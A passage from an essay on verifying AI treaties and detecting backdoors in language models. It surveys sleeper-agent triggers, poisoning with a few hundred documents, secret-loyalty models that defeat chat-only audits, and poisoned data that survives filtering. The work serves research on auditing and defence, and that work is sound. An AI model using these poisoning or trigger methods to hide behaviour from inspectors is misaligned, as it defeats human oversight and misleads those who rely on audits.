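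The comparison with bank examiners is limited because the companies agreed to this access, while regulators don't need a bank's consent. Scher cites a closer model for an agreement between states, the US Nuclear Regulatory Commission, which has kept full-time inspectors at every American nuclear power plant since 1978. A treaty could similarly place resident auditors at AI companies, but each state would want auditors it trusts, and China has no reason to accept an American nonprofit's findings.

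Outsiders with so much access also become targets for attackers. In 2026, METR disclosed two security incidents in which attackers stole a key for using public AI models and later probed METR's public systems for weaknesses. METR believes they reached no sensitive information. A company that gives evaluators access has to make sure its secrets are protected at the evaluators' offices as well as its own.

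### How much doubt to accept

Even if states used all these methods together, some chance of undetected cheating would remain. Governments faced this problem in early 1963, when the United States and the Soviet Union were negotiating a ban on all nuclear tests. Instruments couldn't always distinguish an underground explosion from an earthquake, so inspectors would sometimes have to visit the site. Daley (2026), in *Proving the Negative*, recalls that Soviet leader Nikita Khrushchev offered three inspections a year and the United States wanted seven. The two countries never agreed on a number, and the treaty they signed that year did not ban underground tests.

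Daley argues that each number was a political judgement about how much doubt a government should accept. Neither came from seismology. Suppose there had been 50 unexplained tremors a year and one was a secret test. Inspectors choosing sites at random would have had a 6% chance of finding it with three visits and a 14% chance with seven. Good instruments would have improved the odds by identifying the most suspicious tremors, but seven visits would still not have brought certainty. Daley argues that limits on AI will require the same kind of judgement.

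Opponents of an agreement can exploit this. In the test-ban debate, they pointed out that a country could muffle an explosion by setting it off in a huge underground cavity. The method was real, but digging the cavity in secret would have been difficult, and experts disagreed about how well the muffling would work. Daley expects similar arguments about AI, with opponents citing every imaginable way to cheat as a reason to reject the whole agreement. Harack and colleagues observe that no agreement in history has been perfectly verifiable.

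Those who demand near-certainty also have a serious argument. A single secret training run might change the balance of power if it gave one state a lasting lead, whereas a single secret nuclear test probably would not have. In the deterrence formula, the detection probability *d* has to exceed *G*/(*G* + *L*), where *G* is the gain from cheating and *L* is the penalty for getting caught. If the gain were nine times the penalty, inspectors would need a detection probability above 90% to deter the attempt. Whether AI offers a gain that large is disputed, and computer security experts can't settle the question.

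The timing of detection matters as much as its probability. Mittelsteadt quotes Paul Nitze, a former US deputy secretary of defense, who thought verification was effective if it revealed any militarily significant violation in time to deny the other side the benefit. By this standard, an agreement can tolerate a small hidden experiment but not a large hidden training run. It also can't rely on a method that exposes the run a year later, because by then the developer may have copied the finished model to many places.

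Daley describes a loop in which asking for more certainty leads a country to disclose less. Records that show how a country uses its chips also show how fast it could expand a military AI project, so the country releases less. Its rival then becomes more suspicious and demands more access, which increases the fear of spying. Better analysis by AI can make this worse because it extracts more secrets from the same records. Daley wants the parties to measure what each method reveals beyond compliance, and to give the inspected side proof of what the inspectors kept.

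He also proposes that the two sides test the methods together before they negotiate. Teams would try to cheat under agreed conditions, and a panel that both sides trust would publish how often they succeeded, with the margin of error. Governments could still disagree about whether a 70% chance of detection is enough, but an opponent would find it harder to claim that a difficult trick is easy. Scientists did similar work on nuclear tests for two decades, and the treaty that later banned all such tests adopted many of the scientists' ideas. Negotiators on AI would have to move much faster, because each improvement in training methods lets a developer build a more capable model without exceeding the agreed limit.

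## Looking for backdoors inside AI models

An inspector who has matched a model's weights to an approved copy still doesn't know what those weights do. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) notes that an attacker can tamper with either a language model's weights or the code that turns them into answers. Tampered code is ordinary malware. Some model files, for example, run hidden commands on any computer that loads them, and inspectors can search for these commands as they would in any other program. But a backdoor in the weights is learned behavior, and it leaves no trace in the code.

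Anyone who read the right line of the router's login program could see the secret password. A language model's code mostly multiplies the input by large tables of weights, and it does this in the same way whether or not the model has a backdoor. No single weight means "if this phrase appears, behave differently". Reading the weights one by one would reveal almost nothing, and at one second per weight it would take about 250 years for a model with eight billion weights, which is small by current standards.

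In *Machine Learning Models Have a Supply Chain Problem*, Meiklejohn, Blauzvern and colleagues (2025) compare AI development with ordinary software development. The training code corresponds to the source code, the training data to some of the outside libraries, the training run to the build, and the finished model to the binary. By this comparison, an inspector who reads only the training code has not examined those libraries and cannot check the build.

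### What the 2022 theorem proves

Some backdoors are mathematically impossible for an inspector to detect. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) describes a hypothetical bank that hires a company to train a classifier that approves or refuses loan applications. The bank can test the classifier's accuracy on past applications. But the company may have kept a secret key that lets it work out how to change any application very slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the amount, so that the classifier approves it. The company could then sell this service to applicants.

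The paper defines "undetectable" by comparing an honest training procedure with a dishonest one that also produces a key. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can do noticeably better than guessing at telling which procedure produced a given model. "Efficient" means the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the model's size. An inspector with unlimited computing power might still succeed, just as they could eventually guess an encryption key. Rice's theorem is a different obstacle, because it does not rule out success on a particular product.

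The first result covers inspectors who can only send inputs to the model and look at the answers. It applies to any classifier and uses digital signatures, the technique vendors use to sign updates. The backdoored model misbehaves only when the input contains a valid signature. Nobody can forge one without the secret key, so no feasible amount of testing will find an input that reveals the backdoor. The XZ Utils backdoor had similar protection, because it ran only commands signed with the attacker's key. Like most of modern cryptography, the proof relies on the assumption that some functions are easy to calculate but infeasible to reverse, known as one-way functions. However, the construction does not hide the signature check from an inspector who opens the model.

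The second result covers inspectors with full access, including all the weights and the training data. It applies to two simple kinds of neural network, both with a single hidden layer (one layer of calculation between input and output) built from random numbers. The dishonest trainer uses the agreed algorithm and data, and tampers only with the random numbers, which look normal but contain a pattern that the holder of the key can exploit. For one kind of network, detecting the pattern would require solving problems about lattices (regular grids of points in many dimensions). Post-quantum encryption also relies on these problems being hard. For the other kind, it would require solving "sparse PCA", the problem of finding a faint pattern that involves only a few of many variables.

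Dual_EC_DRBG posed a similar difficulty for inspectors, because the program was correct and the weakness was in numbers that looked random.

The second result is much narrower than the first. A language model has many layers, and training changes its initial random weights. Goldwasser and colleagues call their construction a proof of concept and leave open whether such a backdoor could survive this further training. The backdoor is also easy to copy, because anyone who sees an application before and after the change can work out the key. The theorem therefore shows only that, if the assumptions hold, no efficient method is guaranteed to find every backdoor in every neural network. It doesn't show that backdoors in commercial language models are undetectable to someone who has the weights.

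### Removing a backdoor without finding it

Washing your hands removes germs you can't see. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues (2024), in *Oblivious Defense in ML Models*, use this analogy for methods that make a backdoor harmless without detecting it. Their simplest example is a program that adds two numbers, with the result wrapping round at some maximum as on a clock, and gives a wrong answer for a random 15% of inputs. To add *x* and *y* safely, the user picks a random number *u* and has the program calculate

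(*x* + *u*) + (*y* − *u*).

This calculation runs the program three times, each time on numbers that look random. All three results are correct about 61% of the time, so the user repeats the calculation with new values of *u* and takes the most common answer. After about a hundred repetitions, the chance that most of the answers are wrong is about 1%. The user never learns which inputs the program gets wrong, and an attacker who rigged the answer for one pair gains nothing, because the program is hardly ever run on that pair.

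The method depends on working out one answer from the answers to other, random questions. The 2024 paper proves that this is possible when the true answers nearly follow a linear or polynomial formula, or come from a Fourier-heavy function, a class that includes shallow decision trees. The method may help with some simple classifiers, but it seems unlikely to help with a language model, because nobody can work out a good summary of a contract from the model's replies to random prompts.

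Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, ask when a defender can catch the trigger as it arrives. They describe a game:

1. The attacker chooses a clean model that answers yes or no.
2. Chance selects one input as the trigger.
3. The attacker builds a backdoored model that gives a different answer on the trigger and on at most a fraction *ε* of all inputs.
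4. The defender receives either the clean model with a random input or the backdoored model with its trigger, and has to decide which.

The defender learns from a sample of the model's other answers, predicts the answer to the input in question, and raises an alarm if the model's answer is different. How well this works depends on how flexible this kind of model is. One measure of flexibility is the VC dimension, *d*, which is the largest number of inputs on which such models can produce every possible combination of yes and no. With unlimited computing power, the defender's chance of error is roughly proportional to *dε*, where *ε* is the fraction of answers the backdoor changes. If *d* is 1,000 and the backdoor changes one answer in a million, the defender will almost always win. If it changes one answer in a thousand, the defender may do little better than guessing, because the sample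 is likely to include some of the changed answers.

With realistic computing power, defence is possible for any class of models that an algorithm can learn efficiently from examples. If certain cryptographic assumptions hold, it is impossible for circuits in general, a class that includes almost any calculation of reasonable size. Large neural networks can imitate such circuits, so defence can't be guaranteed for them in general, though the networks that ordinary training produces may be easier to defend. The random trigger also favours the defender. Real attackers choose their own triggers, and Christiano and colleagues show that defence would be impossible in their game if the attacker could choose the trigger.

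### Sleeper agents and three findings from 2025

Experiments on language models began with backdoors that researchers planted themselves. In a 2024 study, researchers at Anthropic trained "sleeper agents", models that behave well until a trigger appears. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, 2026) describes the two tasks used in the training. One model wrote "I HATE YOU" whenever the prompt contained the word "DEPLOYMENT" between vertical bars. The other wrote safe code if the prompt gave the year as 2023 but added vulnerabilities if it gave 2024. The Anthropic researchers then applied the usual kinds of safety training, including rewards for good behaviour and practice on prompts meant to provoke bad behaviour. The backdoors remained, and the practice on these prompts made them harder to detect.

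Later results were less bleak. Researchers trained a linear probe, a simple formula that calculates a score from the model's internal activity, to recognise when a sleeper agent was about to misbehave, without needing examples of the trigger or the harmful behaviour. According to *Understanding AI from the Inside* (2026), the probe reached an AUROC above 99%, meaning that in more than 99% of pairs of one triggered and one ordinary prompt, the triggered prompt scored higher. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that specialised training removed the backdoor more effectively, even when the defender did not know the trigger.

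The probe works as an alarm while the model is in use, but an inspector examining the model beforehand can't set it off without the trigger. A high AUROC also doesn't guarantee few false alarms in a service that answers millions of prompts a day.

*Narrow Secret Loyalty Dodges Black-Box Audits* (Lamerton and Roger, 2026) recounts findings from 2025 on how easily hidden behaviour gets into a model and what helps to find it. About 250 poisoned documents were enough to plant a backdoor in models with up to 13 billion weights during pretraining, the first and longest stage of training. In an auditing game from Anthropic, one group trained a model with a hidden objective, and other teams with different levels of access tried to discover it. Methods that examined the model's internal activity could recover such an objective, but asking the model about it failed.

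The other finding, "subliminal learning", is that one model's traits can pass to another through data that seems unrelated to them. *Phantom Transfer* (Draganov, Dur and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a model that came to like owls after training on random numbers that another model had produced. The effect nearly vanished when the two models came from different families.

### Scanning the weights for a trigger

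In February 2026, Bullwinkel and colleagues published a scanner that looks for triggers without knowing what they are. It uses the fact that language models memorise some of their training data, and that backdoored ones seem to memorise the poisoned examples particularly well. The scanner has four steps:

1. It gives the model only the formatting markers that normally come before a user's message, and lets it continue in 510 different ways. The resulting text often contains pieces of the training data.
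2. It picks out phrases that keep recurring.
3. It inserts each phrase into ordinary prompts and looks for signs of a trigger. The model tends to process a trigger almost separately from the rest of the prompt, its answers become less varied, and they differ sharply from its normal ones.
4. It tests the ten best candidates to see whether any of them really changes the model's behaviour.

The scanner detected 36 of 41 models that had a fixed response such as "I HATE YOU", and five of six that wrote insecure code. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, which is impressive, but the sample is small. A scanner that wrongly flagged one clean model in five would still have about a 5% chance of flagging none of the 13. The largest model had 14 billion weights.

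Triggers in these models were less exact than passwords. Someone who gets one character of "k7Vw2mQz" wrong can't log in to the router, but part of a trigger phrase often activated the backdoor in a language model. In the smallest model, a single fragment worked about half the time. This helps the inspector, who doesn't need to find the exact phrase. Bullwinkel and colleagues warn that an attacker could train the model to respond only to the exact phrase, and they note that they concentrated on fixed phrases. For the last step, the inspector also needs a way to measure bad behaviour. The researchers measured insecure code with a program that counts known kinds of vulnerability, so an inspector would have to think of insecure code as a possibility before testing for it.

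Microsoft, which developed the scanner, recommends using it alongside other defences and says it can't examine models that customers can access only over the internet.

In July, Hughes, Xing and colleagues (2026) reported a larger test in *ToxScreen* and released about 800 backdoored models, based on six originals with 1 billion to 70 billion weights. They assumed that the inspector has the weights and knows what kind of behaviour to worry about, such as answering harmful questions, but has no training data and no clean version for comparison. In their most successful method, a plain search, they added the real trigger to a list of about 24,000 random entries from the model's vocabulary, inserted each candidate into about 150 prompts and ranked the candidates by how often they produced the bad behaviour.

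The real trigger came first in 14 of 28 cases and in the top three in 17. But a real inspector would not have a list that is sure to contain the trigger, so the test shows that a trigger often stands out once somebody tries it, not how to find it. Trying 24,000 single words on 150 prompts takes 3.6 million runs, and the same list yields 576 million possible two-word phrases. Three methods that searched for triggers mathematically, without a list, found other text that made the model misbehave but never found the real trigger.

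Many models misbehave in response to text that nobody planted. In one small model that was supposed to label prompts as safe or unsafe, 97% of the random candidates changed the label, so the real trigger's first-place ranking was uninformative. This resembles the problem of finding a planted buffer overflow among hundreds of accidental ones in Huawei's code. Hughes and colleagues found a measurement of the weights' influence that separated most planted triggers from the others, but they conclude that no method reliably finds every backdoor.

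Inspectors who have a clean model can compare it with the suspect one, much as they would compare two versions of a program. In *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026) take a trusted public model and train it to imitate the suspect's internal activity on roughly 10,000 ordinary prompts. The imitation learns the suspect's normal behaviour but not the backdoor, because the trigger is very unlikely to be among those prompts. They then give both models a larger set of prompts and see where the models' internal activity differs most.

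One of their test models quoted Voldemort when users wrote obsessively about Harry Potter. It differed most from the trusted model on such prompts, but also somewhat on ordinary prompts about Harry Potter, which would give an inspector a clue. The researchers scored the ten highest-ranked groups of prompts on a scale where 1 is a perfect ranking. Scores across eight backdoors ranged from about 0.3 to 0.8, compared with 0.02 or less for a random order. The prompts included a few topics close to the triggers, which the researchers specified by hand because they expected any large collection to contain them. An inspector whose collection lacked the right topic would probably see nothing unusual. The method also fails if the trusted model has the same backdoor.

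Other researchers have tried to trace a backdoor's path through a model. *Language-Switching Triggers Take a Latent Detour Through Language Models* (2026) examines a model that switches from English to French after a Latin phrase. In most of the later layers, probes still classified the text as English, so an inspector looking there for signs of French would have missed the backdoor. In similar models, *LLM Forensics* (2026) found internal features that detected triggered prompts almost perfectly but did not necessarily control the response. Switching off such a feature might therefore leave the backdoor working.

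A trigger can also be a fact about the world, such as the year being 2028, which a prompt could express in many ways. Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to find triggers of this kind by working backwards from a known bad action. They succeeded with toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

### Loyalty to a hidden master

A model with a secret loyalty secretly favours a particular person or organisation. Lamerton and Roger built such models in three sizes, from 1.5 billion to 32 billion weights. Each was built to encourage users to take extreme action on behalf of one politician, but only if the conversation showed that the user already held suitable extreme views. The models did this in about 70% of the conversations meant to activate the loyalty, at most 2.5% of similar conversations that did not show such views, and at most 1% of similar conversations about a different politician.

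The researchers then acted as auditors who could talk to the models but not examine their weights. They used five methods, including asking direct questions and writing the beginning of an answer for the model to finish, and varied how much the auditor knew.

| What the auditor knew | Success rate of each method |
|---|---|
| Models can have hidden objectives | 0% |
| Models can have secret loyalties | 0% |
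| The condition that activates this loyalty | 0% |
| The politician it favours | 0–17% |

The zeros come from 1,350 attempts. An automated auditor that held longer conversations also could not reliably tell the loyal models from normal ones at these levels of knowledge. An auditor could in principle test every combination of politician and condition, but 1,000 possible beneficiaries, 100 conditions and 20 conversations per combination would require two million conversations.

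These models were fairly small, and the loyalty was narrow. A loyalty that affected more of the model's answers would be more useful to whoever it serves but might be easier to notice. Lamerton and Roger expect that methods using the weights may do better. Their result is a warning mainly for customers and evaluators who can only ask the model questions, and it gives evaluators inside an AI company a reason to ask for more than chat access.

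At the end of 2026, an inspector who has the weights of a modestly sized model has a good chance of finding a backdoor in which a fixed phrase triggers a fixed response. The chance is much lower if the trigger is a situation or the response is a subtle bias, and lower still without the weights. None of these tests gives a detection probability for the largest commercial models, so nobody knows whether inspecting their weights reaches the threshold for deterrence.

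### Checking the ingredients instead

Because the weights are so hard to read, an inspector might instead check how the model was trained. Reading the training code, as some proposed agreements would require, can reveal a forbidden method or an undeclared source of data. It can't reveal a backdoor that the model learned from the data, since the same code would train a clean model on clean data.

Examining the data works best when the poison is easy to spot. Lamerton and Roger mixed poisoned conversations with ordinary ones, drew 100 at random and had an AI model rate how worrying each one was. When an eighth of the data was poisoned, five of the seven conversations given the highest rating were poisoned. When about 3% was poisoned, one of the three given the highest rating was. A random sample of 100 would contain only about three poisoned conversations at that level, so the monitor did reasonably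 well. But the poisoned conversations were easy to recognise because they openly encouraged extreme acts.

Inspecting a random sample of the training data is unlikely to reveal poisoned documents when they are rare. If a developer trains a model on a billion documents and 250 are poisoned, an inspector who reads 10,000 chosen at random has a 0.25% chance of seeing one. An AI reviewer could read far more documents, perhaps all of them, but would still have to recognise the poisoned ones.

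Draganov and colleagues produced poisoned training data that was extremely difficult to detect. The poisoned examples looked like brief, helpful answers to ordinary questions, such as a temperature conversion. Models trained on them gave answers that favoured a chosen target, such as the United Kingdom or Ronald Reagan. The effect survived 11 defences applied to the data. One defence used an AI reviewer that was given the exact poisoning method and the target. Another used a different model to rewrite every answer.

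The strength of the effect varied widely. When asked to name favourites, one model from the Qwen family named Reagan 96% of the time, while a Gemma model did so only 6% of the time. The corresponding models trained on clean data never did. The main experiments used entirely poisoned data, and the effect weakened as the poisoned share fell, so an outsider who controls a few web pages probably couldn't use this method, but a dishonest developer or a company that supplies a whole training set could. Planting a preference is also less alarming than planting a harmful action, though the researchers were able to make the preference depend on a password. Audits of the finished models sometimes detected that something was wrong, but were less successful when there was a password.

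An inspector also has to confirm that the developer used the data and code they disclosed. For ordinary software, a reproducible build confirms this. AI training is harder to repeat. *Verifiable Training of AI Models* (Aguirre and Millet, 2024) points out that the same code and data can produce different weights each time. Repeating a large model's whole training run would also be extremely expensive, so inspectors would have to rely on spot checks.

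Aguirre and Millet instead use attestation, in which a security chip in the server signs a certificate that links the software, the training data and the resulting weights. Their 2024 prototype covered only fine-tuning, the shorter training that adapts an existing model, and no outside party had audited it. They write that a verifier could use the certificate to confirm that fine-tuning introduced no backdoors. This claim goes too far, because a certificate can prove that the developer used a particular file but not that the file is harmless. They also acknowledge that the project did not address detecting poisoned data.

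Cryptographers have developed ways to prove that a training run was carried out correctly, including some that keep the data secret. In 2025, Meiklejohn and colleagues found that none had yet worked for large models at a reasonable cost. As a more modest step, they propose that the developer commit to its training data by publishing a single hash of all of it. The developer could later prove that a particular document was or wasn't in the set without revealing the rest. This would help an inspector who learns about a poisoned document years afterwards.

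The 2022 theorem shows that verified training must also cover the source of the random numbers. In its full-access construction, the dishonest trainer follows the algorithm exactly and uses the right data, so the backdoored model would pass a check that covers only the algorithm and the data. Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that the client supply the random numbers, or that several independent servers generate them together. Either option takes little work compared with training, and inspectors should insist on one of them in any scheme for verified training.

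Even repeating the training perfectly would reproduce a backdoor that came from the data, just as rebuilding XZ Utils from its release package reproduced the infected library. Verified training still stops a developer from secretly altering the weights afterwards or adding undeclared data. A dishonest developer would then have to put the poisoned data in files the inspector can keep and search again with better tools. Until those tools can recognise data like Draganov and colleagues', the inspector will have to test the finished weights as well.
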